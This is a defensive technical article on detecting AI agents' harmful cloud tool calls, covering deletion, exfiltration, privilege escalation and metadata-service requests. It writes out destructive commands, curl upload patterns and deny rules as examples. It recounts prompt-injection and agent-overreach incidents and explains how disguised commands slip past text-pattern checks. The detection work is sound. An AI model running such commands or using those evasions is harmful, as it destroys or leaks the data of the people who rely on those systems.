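# Detecting harmful tool calls by AI agents: cloud deletion, data exfiltration, privilege escalation and requests to cloud metadata addresses

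## The four kinds of harmful tool call and how they differ

To detect harmful tool calls, security software examines each action an AI agent is about to take, and blocks those that would do damage or holds them for a person to review. An AI agent is a program in which a language model chooses the actions and other software carries them out. The model produces only text, so to act it writes a tool call, a structured request that names a tool (such as a shell, a web client or a cloud interface) and supplies the arguments. The detector checks this request before the program around the model runs it. After running a request, the program returns the output as text, which the model uses to write its next request.

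Four kinds of tool call cause most of the damage in a cloud account, which holds a company's rented machines, storage and databases. They delete resources, send data out, widen permissions, or fetch credentials from the metadata service, an address that software can reach from inside a cloud machine.

### From a command to a cloud account

Customers of Amazon Web Services (AWS), Microsoft Azure or Google Cloud manage what they rent through the provider's API, a set of named operations that programs call over the network. Suppose an agent runs `aws ec2 terminate-instances` in its shell with the identifier of a virtual machine, or "instance". The `aws` program finds credentials in a file, an environment variable or the metadata service, then signs a request for the TerminateInstances operation with a secret key and sends it. The provider uses the signature to identify the caller, checks the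 caller's permissions, and performs or refuses the operation. A Python script, a deployment tool such as Terraform, or an MCP server (a program that offers tools to an agent over the Model Context Protocol) can call the same operation, so a detector may see the same action in many forms.

The provider's identity and access management (IAM) system stores identities and the policies that list what each may do. A user identity often has long-lived keys. *Additional IAM Roles Creation*, from the financial industry's open-source foundation, FINOS, defines a role as an identity for applications or services. Another identity can assume a role temporarily, for example to gain a privilege it does not normally hold.

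The cloud provider can't tell from a request whether a person or an agent chose the command. If a developer starts an agent in a terminal that holds administrator keys, the agent's requests are signed with those keys. Security engineers call this inherited power ambient authority. In *Security Risks in Tool-Enabled AI Agents*, Goel (2026) writes that a cloud-hosted agent may inherit credentials, the right to execute commands, access to internal networks, and the ability to change shared files, databases and settings. Goel defines an agent as a tuple A = (M, T, E, P), where M is the model, T its tools, E the execution environment and P the available privileges. Risk arises when P exceeds the minimum the task requires and the agent can use those privileges through T.

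A sandbox around the agent does not always bound P. If the agent can trigger a company's build pipeline, its scripts run in the pipeline's environment, which may hold production credentials. An instruction in the prompt to leave production alone does not remove anything from P.

### The four classes

Deletion is the simplest kind, in which the agent terminates an instance or deletes a bucket (a container for stored files). MITRE's *Data Destruction* (2019), an entry in the American non-profit's catalogue of attack techniques, adds machine images, database instances, snapshots and volumes to the list of targets. The severity depends on the backups. According to WithSecure's *Cloud Asset Destruction*, the damage may be irreparable if the access used for the deletion also extends to backups and older versions.

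In data exfiltration, the agent sends data, such as a customer table, to a host outside the company. It needs no special tool for this, because any tool that writes somewhere can carry the data in its arguments. MITRE's *Exfiltration via AI Agent Tool Invocation* lists emails, edited documents, updated customer records and generated images as possible carriers.

In privilege escalation, the agent changes who has which permissions, for example by attaching an administrator policy to an identity, most simply its own. On AWS, a single AttachUserPolicy call does this. MITRE's *Account Manipulation* (2020) also names CreatePolicyVersion, which creates a new version of an existing policy. In Kubernetes, which many companies use to run their containers, the equivalent is a RoleBinding or ClusterRoleBinding, an object that grants a set of permissions to an account.

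A metadata request is a fetch of 169.254.169.254, the address of a service that cloud providers run so that code on a machine can look up facts about that machine. Much of this information, such as the region or the network addresses, is more or less harmless (Ullrich, 2026, *Simple Scans for Cloud Metadata Service*), but the service also returns credentials for IAM roles. The Center for Threat-Informed Defense's *T1552.005 Cloud Instance Metadata API Mappings* describes two ways to get them. Someone already on the machine can query the address directly, or an outsider can use server-side request forgery (SSRF), which makes a server send a request that the outsider could not. An agent with a web-fetching tool on a cloud machine opens both routes, because it runs on the machine and fetches addresses that other people's text may suggest.

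| Class | What it harms | Can anyone undo it? | What gives it away | Legitimate action that looks the same |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Deletion | Availability of systems and data | Only from backups or retained versions | The operation, its target and how much it covers | Tearing down a test environment |
| Exfiltration | Confidentiality | No; a company can replace a leaked key but cannot recall a leaked table | The data and the destination | Sending a report to a customer or a backup to a partner |
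| Privilege escalation | Control of the account | The grant, yes; what the identity did with it, perhaps not | The identity that gains and the permissions it gains | Setting up a new service or a new colleague |
| Metadata request | Secrecy of the machine's credentials | Not the read itself; the credentials expire | The network address that the request reaches | A cloud library fetching its own credentials |

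Most of the work in detection comes from the last column. Elastic's *Suspicious Instance Metadata Service (IMDS) API Request*, a rule for security-monitoring software, exempts helper processes of the code editors VS Code and Cursor. That is reasonable for general monitoring. But Cursor also runs coding agents, so a team that copied the exemption into an agent detector might exempt the process it meant to watch.

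### Why one "dangerous command" rule fails

A first detector is often a list of dangerous commands. Adversa AI's vendor guide *OWASP ASI02* gives a typical example, with text patterns for wiping file systems, dropping database tables, destroying cloud resources and reading credential files. The list has no patterns for sending data out, granting permissions or contacting the metadata address. Its pattern for terminating instances matches every termination, whether the machine is left over from last night's tests or is the production database server. Its pattern for removing a bucket matches only if the force flag comes right after the verb, but people normally put the bucket's name there.

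More patterns would fill the gaps, but they would still be imprecise, because the verb alone rarely shows whether a call does harm. Adversa AI gives the example of a `delete_database` tool, which is harmless when used on a test database but ruinous when used on the production one.

Whether a deletion is harmful depends on which resources it removes, how many, and whether anyone relies on them. MITRE's *Detection Strategy for Modify Cloud Compute Infrastructure* (2025) also uses context from the logs, and treats an instance deletion as more suspicious when it happens soon after the instance was created or comes from a new or rarely used account. These signals suit human accounts better than agents. For example, a coding agent may create a test machine, run a test and delete the machine ten minutes later during normal work, which matches the first signal.

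A tool call is exfiltration when it sends sensitive data to an outside destination. An agent may send public documentation to any host, or a customer table to the company's own storage, without causing this harm. A rule that only looks for `curl` commands checks neither the sensitivity of the data nor the destination.

Privilege escalation gives an identity permissions it didn't have before, where a permission is an operation it can perform on a particular resource. Attaching a read-only policy to a new service adds a few permissions. Attaching an administrator policy adds nearly all of them, unless the identity was already an administrator, in which case it adds none. The command's text doesn't show which permissions the identity already had, so a detection rule has to look them up in the account.

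Whether a tool call is a metadata request depends on the resolved address, which is the numeric address the machine will connect to. A web address usually contains a name, which can resolve to any numeric address, so a rule that searches the text of the call for 169.254.169.254 can miss requests that go there.

### Three causes, one rule

Agents make harmful calls by mistake, by exceeding their task, or through prompt injection, in which text the agent reads makes it follow someone else's instructions. Adversa AI describes a mistake from December 2025, when a developer asked Google's Antigravity coding assistant to clear a project's cache and the agent erased the whole D: drive. In July 2025, Replit's assistant exceeded its task by deleting a production database after the user had told it to freeze all changes. PromptRiskDB's *Data Destruction via AI Agent Tool Invocation* describes an October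 2024 demonstration of prompt injection in which researchers at the security company HiddenLayer hid instructions in a PDF. When a user asked Anthropic's Claude to work with the file, the model called its shell to delete the file system.

Accounts of such cases need some care, because they may describe an attempted deletion rather than a completed one. Adversa AI lists Amazon's coding assistant Q among its catastrophic incidents of 2025 because an attacker planted a prompt in the assistant's editor extension that told the agent to delete files and cloud resources, and Amazon released the extension with the prompt in it. Luckily, a syntax error kept the planted code from executing, so it harmed no customer environment, according to the AWS finding quoted in PromptRiskDB's record.

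Goel gave an agent built on OpenAI's GPT-5.1 five tools and ran it ten times in each of four scenarios, first without defences and then with light ones. Without defences, the agent used the shell where file tools would have done in 40% of runs, and followed instructions planted in repository files in 90%. It behaved unsafely in every run of the other two scenarios, one involving secrets in environment variables and the other pipeline scripts that send secrets out. These figures support the claim that the problem is easy to produce, but little more. With ten runs, an observed rate of 40% is consistent with a true rate between about 12% and 74%. Goel also counts any action beyond the intended scope as unsafe, though using a shell to read a file harms nobody by itself, and GPT-5.1 is no longer a leading model.

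A TerminateInstances call with a given identifier removes the same machine whether the model misread its user, overstepped its authority, or followed instructions in a stranger's PDF, and the request doesn't record why it was made. A rule on the action therefore covers all three cases without having to infer the model's intentions.

The cause still matters for investigation and testing. Investigators need to know it after an incident because a poisoned document will trigger the next agent that reads it. In testing, a detector's miss rate on honest mistakes will probably be lower than its miss rate on injected calls, because mistakes use ordinary spellings and an attacker who knows the rules can pick unusual ones.

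### Labelling a call that fits two classes

Making a bucket public looks like escalation because it changes a policy, and like exfiltration because it exposes files to strangers. A workable convention is to label each call by its immediate effect. A call is exfiltration if it lets outsiders read data, escalation if it gives an identity power to act in the account, and deletion if it destroys something.

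By this test, opening a bucket to public reading counts as exfiltration, even before anyone downloads a file. MITRE also classifies such changes as exfiltration, and its *Transfer Data to Cloud Account* (2019) covers anonymous sharing links, shared snapshots and updates to bucket policies. Granting a role to an account outside the company counts as escalation. A lifecycle rule that makes every object in a bucket expire is a settings change in form, but it counts as deletion because it removes the files. For that reason, MITRE recommends limiting who may set such rules. Asking a secrets manager for a password resembles a metadata request but goes to a different service, and MITRE covers it separately in *Credentials from Password Stores* (2023).

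Some calls, such as setting a policy that lets the public both read and overwrite a bucket, fit two classes under any labeling convention. For these calls, the detector should run the rules for both classes and apply the stricter verdict. The main label is for counting and reporting, and a dispute over it should never affect whether the call runs.

### Identifiers in the public catalogues

Security teams share findings by citing catalogue numbers. MITRE maintains two relevant catalogues. ATT&CK covers attacks on ordinary company systems, and *ATLAS* (2020) covers attacks on and through AI systems.

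| Class | ATT&CK | ATLAS |
|---|---|---|
| Deletion | T1485 Data Destruction | AML.T0101 Data Destruction via AI Agent Tool Invocation |
| Exfiltration | T1537 Transfer Data to Cloud Account, for transfers and sharing within one provider | AML.T0086 Exfiltration via AI Agent Tool Invocation |
| Privilege escalation | T1098.003 Additional Cloud Roles; T1098.006 Additional Container Cluster Roles, for Kubernetes | AML.T0053 AI Agent Tool Invocation |
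| Metadata request | T1552.005 Cloud Instance Metadata API | AML.T0055 Unsecured Credentials |

The ATLAS entries for deletion and exfiltration describe those calls almost exactly, but the other two are broader. AML.T0053 covers much more than privilege escalation, since it includes any use of an agent's tools by an adversary and mentions increased privileges as one result. AML.T0055 covers badly stored credentials in general. In ATT&CK, T1537 does not cover a plain post to an outside web host. MITRE has a separate exfiltration entry for data sent to a webhook, an address where a web service accepts incoming messages.

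Both catalogues also assume an adversary is acting, which isn't true when an agent makes an honest mistake. ATT&CK lists deleting an instance under both data destruction (T1485) and a technique for hiding evidence, depending on the attacker's purpose. T1485 is the safer default for a rule based only on the action.

The third reference point is ASI02, "Tool Misuse and Exploitation", the second entry in the 2025 list of agent risks from OWASP, a software security non-profit. According to Adversa AI, it covers both unintentional misuse and deliberate exploitation of legitimate tools, so it applies to all three causes. Because all four classes fall under it, it can't be used to distinguish them.

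Each mapping should include the version number of the catalogue it uses. MITRE's *Updates* (2026) for April record that version 19 of ATT&CK split the Defense Evasion tactic in two. MITRE's *Updates* (2026) for October list version 20 as current, with new AI-related techniques.

### Two error rates

A detector gives one of four verdicts on each tool call: allow, warn, ask a person, or block. Two rates measure how often it is wrong.

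- False positive rate = harmless calls that the detector does not simply allow ÷ all harmless calls
- False negative rate = calls that it should block but lets through ⁠÷ all calls that it should block

A needless warning counts as a false positive, because it takes up somebody's attention. A warning on a call that should have been blocked counts as a false negative, because the call still runs. Asking a person first pauses the call, so it is not yet a miss, although the person may still approve the call. Deleting an old production bucket may be what the owner wants and still merit a question first. A test set should keep such calls separate, with "ask" as the right answer, and count them in neither the false positive rate nor the false negative rate.

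The false positive rate is a share of harmless calls, while the false negative rate is a share of harmful calls, which are far rarer in practice. Suppose an agent makes 10,000 calls, of which the detector should block 20. With a false positive rate of 1%, the detector wrongly blocks about 100 harmless calls. With a false negative rate of 10%, it blocks 18 harmful calls and lets 2 run. Although both rates may seem acceptable, only about 15% of the blocked calls are harmful.

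## Putting a tool call into a form that rules can check

A tool call to a cloud provider starts as text from the model, then becomes the arguments of a tool, network traffic and a named API operation. A detector can examine the call in any of these forms, and its designer has to choose which before writing rules.

### Where to check the call

Several coding agents let the user attach a program, called a hook, that runs just before a tool call. Anthropic's Claude Code passes the tool's input to the hook as JSON, a text format with named fields, and cancels the call if the hook denies it. In Anthropic's toolkit for building agents, a hook can also change the input before the tool runs. GitHub recommends its own version of the hook for policies that depend on the arguments of a single call.

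For a shell tool, one of those arguments is the command line, so a hook receives the command text together with the structured arguments. A rule can directly check a call to a tool named `terminate_instance` that has a field for the machine's identifier, but a shell line has to be parsed first because it may hold several commands, variables and redirections.

| Where | What is visible | What is hidden | Can the detector still stop the call? |
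|---|---|---|---|
| Command text | The whole line that the model wrote | Values of variables, contents of scripts | Yes, before anything runs |
| Structured arguments | The tool's name, and each argument in its own field | What the tool does with the arguments | Yes, before anything runs |
| Network proxy | The destination, and the request itself if the proxy can decrypt it | Local actions, the user's instructions | Yes, but the program has started and may have done other things |
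| Cloud API | The operation, its target and the identity | The command and the conversation behind it | Only through permissions, because log entries come afterwards |

A network proxy relays a machine's outbound traffic. Connections to cloud providers are encrypted, and a proxy that can't decrypt them can read little beyond the host name. On AWS, requests to list virtual machines and to terminate them go to the same host, so such a proxy can block the whole service but can't block only the termination requests.

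A proxy also has no effect on traffic that bypasses it. Agent makers often enforce network limits through a sandbox. Cursor's *run modes* describes a sandbox that blocks network access by default, but commands that need full access run outside it once the user approves. In the example configuration in Snowflake's *Cortex Code CLI sandbox*, `docker` and `kubectl` always run outside the sandbox and follow only the ordinary permission rules. A team that copies this configuration therefore has no sandbox around `kubectl`, the standard command for managing Kubernetes, which can delete the team's cluster.

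The cloud API gives the clearest record of an action, because every tool that terminates an instance ends up sending the same request. But the provider can refuse that request only if the identity lacks permission, and the log entry appears after the provider has handled it. *ClawSentry* (Wang, Wei and colleagues, 2026) describes an open-source monitor that checks actions both before and after they run. The agent waits for the monitor's decision before it acts. Once the action has run, the monitor can only report, because common coding agents have no hook for withdrawing a result that a tool has already returned.

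The tool call is the best place to apply the rules because it is the only point where a detector can identify the session, read the whole request, and block it before it runs. Lecture slides from UT Austin distinguish between what an agent can access and when it must ask for approval. Rules on tool calls are mainly useful for deciding when the agent must ask, while limits on what it can access should be set in the operating system, the network and the cloud account.

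### The record of a call

Rules need the same fields for every call, whichever tool the agent uses. *AgentTrust* (Yang, 2026), an open-source program that checks tool calls before they run, defines an action as a tuple a = (τ, κ, δ, π, ρ, σ, θ).

| Symbol | Field | Example |
|---|---|---|
| τ | Action type, one of eleven | Shell command |
| κ | Tool name | Bash |
| δ | Description in ordinary language | "Remove old test machines" |
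| π | Parameters, by name | The command and a time limit |
| ρ | Raw text | The full command line |
| σ | Session identifier (optional) | s-41 |
| θ | Time, in UTC | 2026-10-07 09:14:03 |

The raw text should stay in the record even after a parser has split it into fields, because investigators will want it and the parser may have made a mistake. The session identifier should be required, because without it nobody can connect a harmless-looking call to the ones before it.

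A detector should never use a tool call's description to make its verdict less severe. The model usually writes the description, so a prompt injection that can change the command can change the description too.

Yang's tuple has no field for the working directory, though the hook records in GitHub's *cli hooks reference* and Anthropic's documentation both include one. Cloud work often depends on this directory. For example, `terraform destroy` names no resource and deletes whatever the configuration in the current directory manages. A record for cloud rules also needs the account, region and identity that the call will use.

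Yang's list of action types mixes forms, such as "shell command", with effects, such as "credential access", and each action has only one type. A shell command that prints a credentials file fits both types. If the hook labels it a shell command, a rule restricted to credential access will not apply to it. To avoid this, either the rule has to list both types or the record has to hold form and effect in separate fields.

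Wang and colleagues use a small adapter for each of four coding agents (Codex, Claude Code, Kimi CLI and Gemini CLI) to convert the agent's own messages into a common event format. The monitor then determines the capability each call requests, its target and its scope, so the same rules can apply to a shell command, a helper script and a built-in tool that have the same effect. A team writes each rule once and needs only a new adapter to add another agent.

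### The parts of a rule

A rule in AgentTrust is also a tuple: an identifier, a name, a description, a set of action types, a regular expression (a notation for text patterns), a risk level, a verdict and tags. The example rule that Wang and colleagues give in YAML, a plain-text format for settings, has slightly different parts.

| Part | AgentTrust | ClawSentry's example |
|---|---|---|
| Identifier | An id, a name and a description | ASI02-001, in the category of tool misuse |
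| Where it applies | A set of action types | Tools named `bash`, `shell` or `exec` |
| Pattern | One regular expression | `curl.*--upload-file`, with a weight of 8 |
| Severity | None, low, medium, high or critical | Critical |
| Verdict | Allow, warn, block or review | None in the rule, as the monitor decides |
| Exemptions | None | Paths that fit `*/test_*` or `*/ci/*` |

Yang's "review" sends the call to a person or to a further policy, so it mostly corresponds to "ask". Severity is separate from the verdict because it describes how bad the action would be and helps people sort reports, while the verdict determines what happens to the call. A critical deletion may still deserve "ask" if the owner often has good reason for it.

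The pattern in ClawSentry's example matches any text that contains `curl` and, later, `--upload-file`. Like most text patterns, it misses equivalent commands, such as those using the option's one-letter form, and matches harmless text, such as a note that mentions `curl --upload-file`.

### How an exemption can hide a harmful call

Exemptions exist because tests and build jobs set off many false alarms. Suppose a developer copies real customer records into `shop/test_customers.csv` to reproduce a bug, and the agent later uploads that file to an outside host. The command matches the pattern in ClawSentry's example. If the exemption compares the uploaded file's path, the exemption matches too, so the rule does nothing and the records leave the company.

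The exemption fails because the path doesn't show what the file contains or where it is going. The agent can also choose file names, so it can trigger the exemption by accident or because of injected text. Exempting the folder for build jobs (`ci`, short for continuous integration) is even riskier because a build pipeline may hold production credentials.

A safer exemption depends on a fact that the agent can't change, such as the number of the cloud account or an approved destination. Wang and colleagues follow this principle in another part of ClawSentry, where only the operator's own channels can declare that a session needs access to a particular target. Several smaller precautions also help:

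- The exemption applies to one named rule and has an end date.
- It lowers the verdict by a step, for example from block to ask, instead of switching the rule off.
- The detector logs every use, so that someone notices when an exemption meant for ten calls a week covers a thousand.

Claude Code is stricter. According to Anthropic's documentation on permissions, it checks deny rules first, then ask rules, then allow rules, and the first match decides. If a user denies `aws *`, a narrower rule that allows `aws s3 ls` has no effect. Users can write exceptions to a deny rule for file paths, but only in the same settings source, so a project's settings file can't cancel a denial that the organisation imposes. Authors must therefore keep deny rules for commands narrow, because they can't exempt useful commands from a broad one.

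### From raw text to a match

Suppose an agent proposes this line:

```
cd infra && AWS_PROFILE=prod timeout 60 aws --region eu-west-1 ec2 terminate-instances --instance-ids i-0a1 i-0b2
```

A detector can turn it into something comparable in five steps.

1. Split the line into commands. The `&&` separates `cd infra` from the rest. Claude Code also splits at `||`, `;`, `|`, `|&`, `&` and line breaks, and applies deny and ask rules to commands nested inside loops or substitutions. The detector carries the new directory forward, because the next command will run there.
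2. Remove wrappers. `timeout 60` only limits how long the real command may run. Claude Code strips a fixed list of such programs before matching, including `time`, `nice` and `nohup`.
3. Save the variable assignment. `AWS_PROFILE=prod` selects a stored set of credentials, and so determines which account loses its machines. A detector that threw the assignment away would lose the most important fact in the line.
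4. Parse what remains. The program is `aws`, the region is `eu-west-1`, the service is `ec2`, the verb is `terminate-instances`, and the flag `--instance-ids` holds two targets.
5. Fill in what the text leaves out. The detector looks up the account number behind the profile `prod`, using a copy of the configuration that the agent can't edit. If the line had no region, the detector would add the default.

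Now a rule can compare fields. This one combines the parts from both systems:

```
id: DEL-EC2-01
action_types: [shell_command, api_call]
match:
  service: ec2
  operation: TerminateInstances
severity: high
verdict: ask
exemptions:
  - account: "111122223333"   # the test account
    verdict: allow
```

The rule matches and the account is not the test account, so the detector refers the call to a person. The rule's match condition doesn't name a program, so the rule also covers an MCP tool that terminates instances, if someone has recorded which operation the tool performs.

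A command line has to be split into its separate commands before rules are matched, because a verdict on the first command doesn't cover the second. An allow rule must accept every command in the line, while a deny rule needs only one harmful command to block it. If Claude Code can't parse part of a command, it doesn't count the command as read-only and asks the user before running it. Any detector should treat a failed parse this way, since the shell may still run a line that the parser can't split. Claude Code also always requires approval for commands longer than 10,000 characters.

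### Why fields are sturdier than strings

A rule that matches text beginning with `aws ec2 terminate-instances` misses the command above because the region option sits between `aws` and `ec2`. A looser pattern that allows any text between the words would catch it, but would also match a harmless `echo` command that writes "never run aws ec2 terminate-instances here" to a notes file. Parsing the command fixes both errors because the rule can then check the program name and ignore the order of the options. It would also fix Adversa AI's pattern for detecting bucket removal, which depended on the position of the force flag.

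Anthropic's documentation for its coding agent calls string patterns that try to constrain a command's arguments "fragile". For example, a rule meant to limit `curl` to GitHub's addresses fails to match if an option comes before the address, or if the address uses another protocol, is stored in a variable, or is a short link that redirects to GitHub. Parsing the command solves the problems with options and protocols, and substituting the variable's value solves the problem with variables. Redirects need a network check because a remote server chooses the final address after the command has started, so it can't be determined from the command's text.

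For the same reason, Anthropic's documentation warns that a deny rule on a shell command covers the form Claude usually writes and "isn't a security boundary around the program". Cursor's *permissions.json reference* calls its lists of pre-approved commands "best-effort convenience". Cursor matches terminal commands by how they begin, so the entry `git` approves `git status` and every other git command. An entry `aws` would likewise approve both listing machines and terminating all of them.

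Web addresses show the advantage of checking fields instead of raw text. Claude Code's web-fetching tool matches rules against the host name alone, ignores capitals and a trailing dot, and doesn't let a wildcard at the end of a name match past a dot. The pattern `example.*` therefore accepts `example.org` but rejects `example.evil.com`, which a plain text search for "example." would let through. A host name doesn't show which numeric address it points to, so checks for metadata requests also have to examine that address.

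A rule can miss a harmful call even when the arguments are structured. Claude Code lets users write deny and ask rules on a single parameter, but it compares the value exactly as the model sent it, and a parameter that the model left out never matches. A rule that asks about calls with `region` set to the production region would miss a call that reaches that region by default. Step 5 above addresses this by filling in the defaults and converting every value to one standard form before comparing. Claude Code does not treat the shell tool's `command` field as an ordinary parameter, because a compound command would get past a single-parameter rule.

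File paths need similar treatment, since a link in one folder can point to a file in another. Claude Code checks both the path that the model requested and the file it leads to. An allow rule applies only if both match, and a deny rule applies if either does. When a call has more than one plausible reading, a detector should likewise allow it only if every reading is acceptable.

### Rewriting text before matching

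Shell commands allow many spellings of one action. Variables, quotation marks and encoded characters all have ordinary uses, but they can also keep a dangerous word out of the text that a rule examines. AgentTrust includes a normaliser that rewrites the command into plainer variants before the rules run. Yang lists nine rewrites, which fall into a few families:

- Two replace names with their meanings, for variables and for aliases (short names for longer commands).
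- Two decode characters that the command gives as numeric codes inside quotation marks.
- Four insert the output of `echo` or `printf` where the command would use it, if that output is literal text.
- One joins neighbouring quoted fragments into a single word.

The normaliser never runs any part of the command. It can safely replace `$(echo rm)` with `rm`, because `echo` with a fixed word always prints that word. It leaves other substitutions alone, because finding their output would mean running code that the detector hasn't checked yet.

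The rules then examine the original text and all its variants. If ρ is the raw text and N(ρ) the set of rewritten variants, the detector works on V = {ρ} ∪ N(ρ). With the verdicts in the order allow < warn < ask < block, the result is

verdict = max { v(R) : rule R matches some x in V }

where v(R) is the verdict in rule R. Because the original stays in the set and the strictest verdict wins, an extra rewrite can make a verdict stricter but never more lenient. It can still cause a false alarm, if a rewrite produces a dangerous-looking command that the shell would never have run. The guarantee also holds only for rules without exemptions. If a rewritten variant could trigger an exemption for the whole call, the rewrite might weaken the verdict after all, so the detector should apply exemptions to each variant separately.

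Yang measured what the normaliser contributes by switching it off and running the same tests again.

| Test set | False negative rate with normaliser | False negative rate without |
|---|---|---|
| 630 scenarios, about 95 of them disguised | 6.4% | 15.7% |
| 300 scenarios, few of them disguised | 5.4% | 5.4% |

The larger set contains 344 calls that the detector should block, so the rates correspond to about 22 misses with the normaliser and 54 without it. Overall accuracy on this set was 95.4% with the normaliser and 90.3% without it, a difference of about 32 scenarios. This matches the difference in misses, which suggests that the normaliser caused few new false alarms, if any. The median check took about 2 milliseconds with or without it.

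The unchanged result on the smaller set shows how much the normaliser's benefit depends on the test. A team that tested only plainly written commands would conclude that it was useless. About 15% of the larger set is disguised, but an agent's everyday work may not contain a similar share. Yang also added rules after seeing which scenarios the detector missed and kept those scenarios in the test, so the 6.4% is probably lower than the rate on new commands. The comparison between the two runs is less affected because both used the same rules.

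The normaliser also missed nested encoding in four scenarios of the smaller set, resolving only the outer layer. To fix this, it could repeat the rewriting until the text stops changing, up to a set number of rounds, and the system should ask a person about anything still unresolved. Yang has so far avoided a full shell parser because it is complex and might tempt developers to evaluate substitutions, but plans to add one. The second risk seems manageable, since a parser can mark a substitution as unknown without evaluating it. A detector benefits from both parsing and rewriting because they do different jobs.

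### Calls whose text does not contain the action

Everything so far depends on the action appearing in the call. When an agent runs `python cleanup.py`, the call names the script but doesn't show the deletion inside it. According to Anthropic's documentation, its file rules cover commands such as `cat` but not a Python or Node script that opens files itself. Zed, which makes another code editor with an agent, likewise describes tool permissions in *Sandboxing* as "of limited use" for a complicated script in a terminal.

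If the agent wrote the script during the session, the detector received its contents in an earlier call and can check them there. It should also record a fingerprint of the file and compare it when the script runs, in case the file has changed. For scripts from elsewhere, the detector can read the file just before it runs. When ClawSentry's rules can't resolve a script, it sends the script to a language model for review and doesn't block it for that reason alone. This is sensible for coding agents, which run scripts often, but the result then depends on how well the model reads code.

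Reading the script may not reveal what it will act on, because a program in a general-purpose language can work out its targets as it runs. Suppose a script lists every snapshot in an account and deletes those older than 30 days. Its text contains no snapshot identifiers, and the number of deletions depends on what the account holds then, so even a perfect parser can't tell whether it will delete three snapshots or three thousand. Yang gives a related example in which `curl` uploads whatever another program feeds into it, so the command's text is the same whether the data is a log file or a list of passwords.

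Cloud providers also publish software development kits (SDKs), libraries that let a program call the cloud API directly. A script that uses an SDK never starts the `aws` program, so rules that look for `aws` commands miss it. A detector can search the script for the library's name and its deletion functions. This catches ordinary code, but a script can evade the search by assembling a function's name from pieces. A stronger remedy is to run general-purpose code without cloud credentials and give the agent a separate tool for cloud operations, with the service, operation and target in separate fields. The rules can then check every cloud call the agent makes. If scripts need credentials, only the provider's permissions can stop a particular operation.

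When a tool is unfamiliar, even the complete arguments may not show what a call does. An MCP server might offer a tool called `sync` that deletes every file missing from a local folder. AgentTrust allows a call by default when no rule or risk pattern matches it, and Claude Code can also let a call proceed when it doesn't meet a hook's conditions. Both defaults suit tools that someone has already examined. For a new tool, the detector should ask for approval until a person has recorded the tool's action type, its effects, and which of its fields holds the target. AgentTrust's default can be changed to "review" for this purpose.

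The same capability may also appear under different tool names. Cowork, Anthropic's agent in the Claude desktop app, runs shell commands through a tool called `mcp__workspace__bash` instead of the usual Bash tool. If a rule denies the whole Bash tool, Claude Code also denies `mcp__workspace__bash`, but it never extends Bash allow rules to that tool. Teams that write their own detectors need a similar list of equivalent tools.

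Finally, a correct rule does nothing if the agent never checks calls against it. In the Cursor forum thread *Command Allowlist is silently ignored when "Auto-Run in Sandbox" is enabled*, a reply confirmed that the list of approved commands had no effect in sandbox mode, although the settings page made it look like a fallback. Claude Code accepts path rules for its Write tool but never matches them, because it checks file access only against path rules for Edit and Read. After every update or change of settings, operators can catch both problems by having the agent attempt a harmless call that a rule should block, such as deleting a machine that doesn't exist, and checking that the detector stops it.

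## Detecting commands that delete cloud resources

A deletion rule needs a list of destructive operations. When a call matches the list, the detector grades it by whether the deleted resources can be restored, how much the call deletes, and whether the target is in production, then uses that grade to set the verdict.

### Listing the operations

Each operation gets a starting grade for reversibility:

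- Grade 1: the resource holds no data of its own, so the team can recreate it from its configuration.
- Grade 2: the provider keeps a copy that someone can restore, often for a limited time.
- Grade 3: only a backup kept elsewhere can bring the data back.

| What goes | AWS | Google Cloud | Azure | Kubernetes | Starting grade |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Machines and running software | TerminateInstances | `gcloud compute instances delete` | `az vm delete` | `kubectl delete deployment` | 1, or 3 if disks go too |
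| Disks | DeleteVolume | `gcloud compute disks delete` | `az disk delete` | `kubectl delete pvc` | 3 |
| Stored files | DeleteObjects | `gcloud storage rm` | `az storage blob delete` | – | 2 if the store keeps old versions, otherwise 3 |
| Databases | DeleteDBInstance | `gcloud sql instances delete` | `az sql db delete` | – | 2 or 3, depending on the options |
| Snapshots | DeleteSnapshot, DeleteDBSnapshot | `gcloud compute snapshots delete` | `az snapshot delete` | `kubectl delete volumesnapshot` | 3 |
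| Encryption keys | ScheduleKeyDeletion | `gcloud kms keys versions destroy` | `az keyvault key delete` | – | 2 during the waiting period |
| A whole group of resources | DeleteStack | `gcloud projects delete` | `az group delete` | `kubectl delete namespace` | The highest grade of anything inside |

A call's options can change its grade. AWS's *DeleteDBInstance* describes two such options. `SkipFinalSnapshot` is off by default, so AWS takes a final snapshot before deleting the database, but `DeleteAutomatedBackups` is on by default, so AWS also deletes the automated backups. Manual snapshots survive either way, but the detector can't rely on them because there may be none.

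A call with the default options therefore gets grade 2, because the final snapshot remains. A call that skips the snapshot gets grade 3 if it also removes the backups and grade 2 if it keeps them, because AWS holds the backups for the retention period that applied when the database was deleted. The sample request in AWS's documentation skips the final snapshot, so an agent that copies it will send a riskier call than the default.

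One common exception is deleting a read replica, a copy that receives updates from another database, because AWS requires callers to skip the snapshot. The original database still holds the data, so the detector should check whether the target is a replica before assigning grade 3.

### Adding scope and environment

The detector adds two adjustments to the starting grade *r*:

score = r + s + e

The scope adjustment *s* is 0 for one named resource and 1 for several resources, a wildcard, a filter or a whole group. The environment adjustment *e* is −2 if the target is in a known test account and +1 otherwise. An unknown environment counts as production because a needless question does much less harm than a lost database.

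| Call | r | s | e | Score | Verdict |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| One machine and its disk, test account | 3 | 0 | −2 | 1 | Allow |
| A group that contains a database, test account | 3 | 1 | −2 | 2 | Warn |
| One Kubernetes deployment, production | 1 | 0 | +1 | 2 | Warn |
| One database with a final snapshot, production | 2 | 0 | +1 | 3 | Ask |
| One disk, environment unknown | 3 | 0 | +1 | 4 | Ask |
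| Every disk that fits a filter, production | 3 | 1 | +1 | 5 | Block |

The numbers are a convention, and a team can change the thresholds, but it matters that the test label is worth three points, more than any other fact about the call. As with exemptions, the detector should take that label from the account number.

Written out in full, the rule looks like this:

```
id: DEL-CLOUD-01
name: Deletion of a cloud resource
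action_types: [shell_command, api_call, network_request, code_execution]
match:
  any:
    - operation_in: destructive_operations
    - operation_words: [delete, destroy, drop, purge,
                        remove, terminate, truncate, wipe]
      operation_not_in: reviewed_operations
severity: high
score:
  reversibility: from destructive_operations, otherwise 3
  scope: 0 for one named target, otherwise 1
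  environment: -2 if account in test_accounts, otherwise 1
verdict:
  up to 1: allow
  2: warn
  3 or 4: ask
  5: block
exemptions: none
tags: [T1485, AML.T0101]
```

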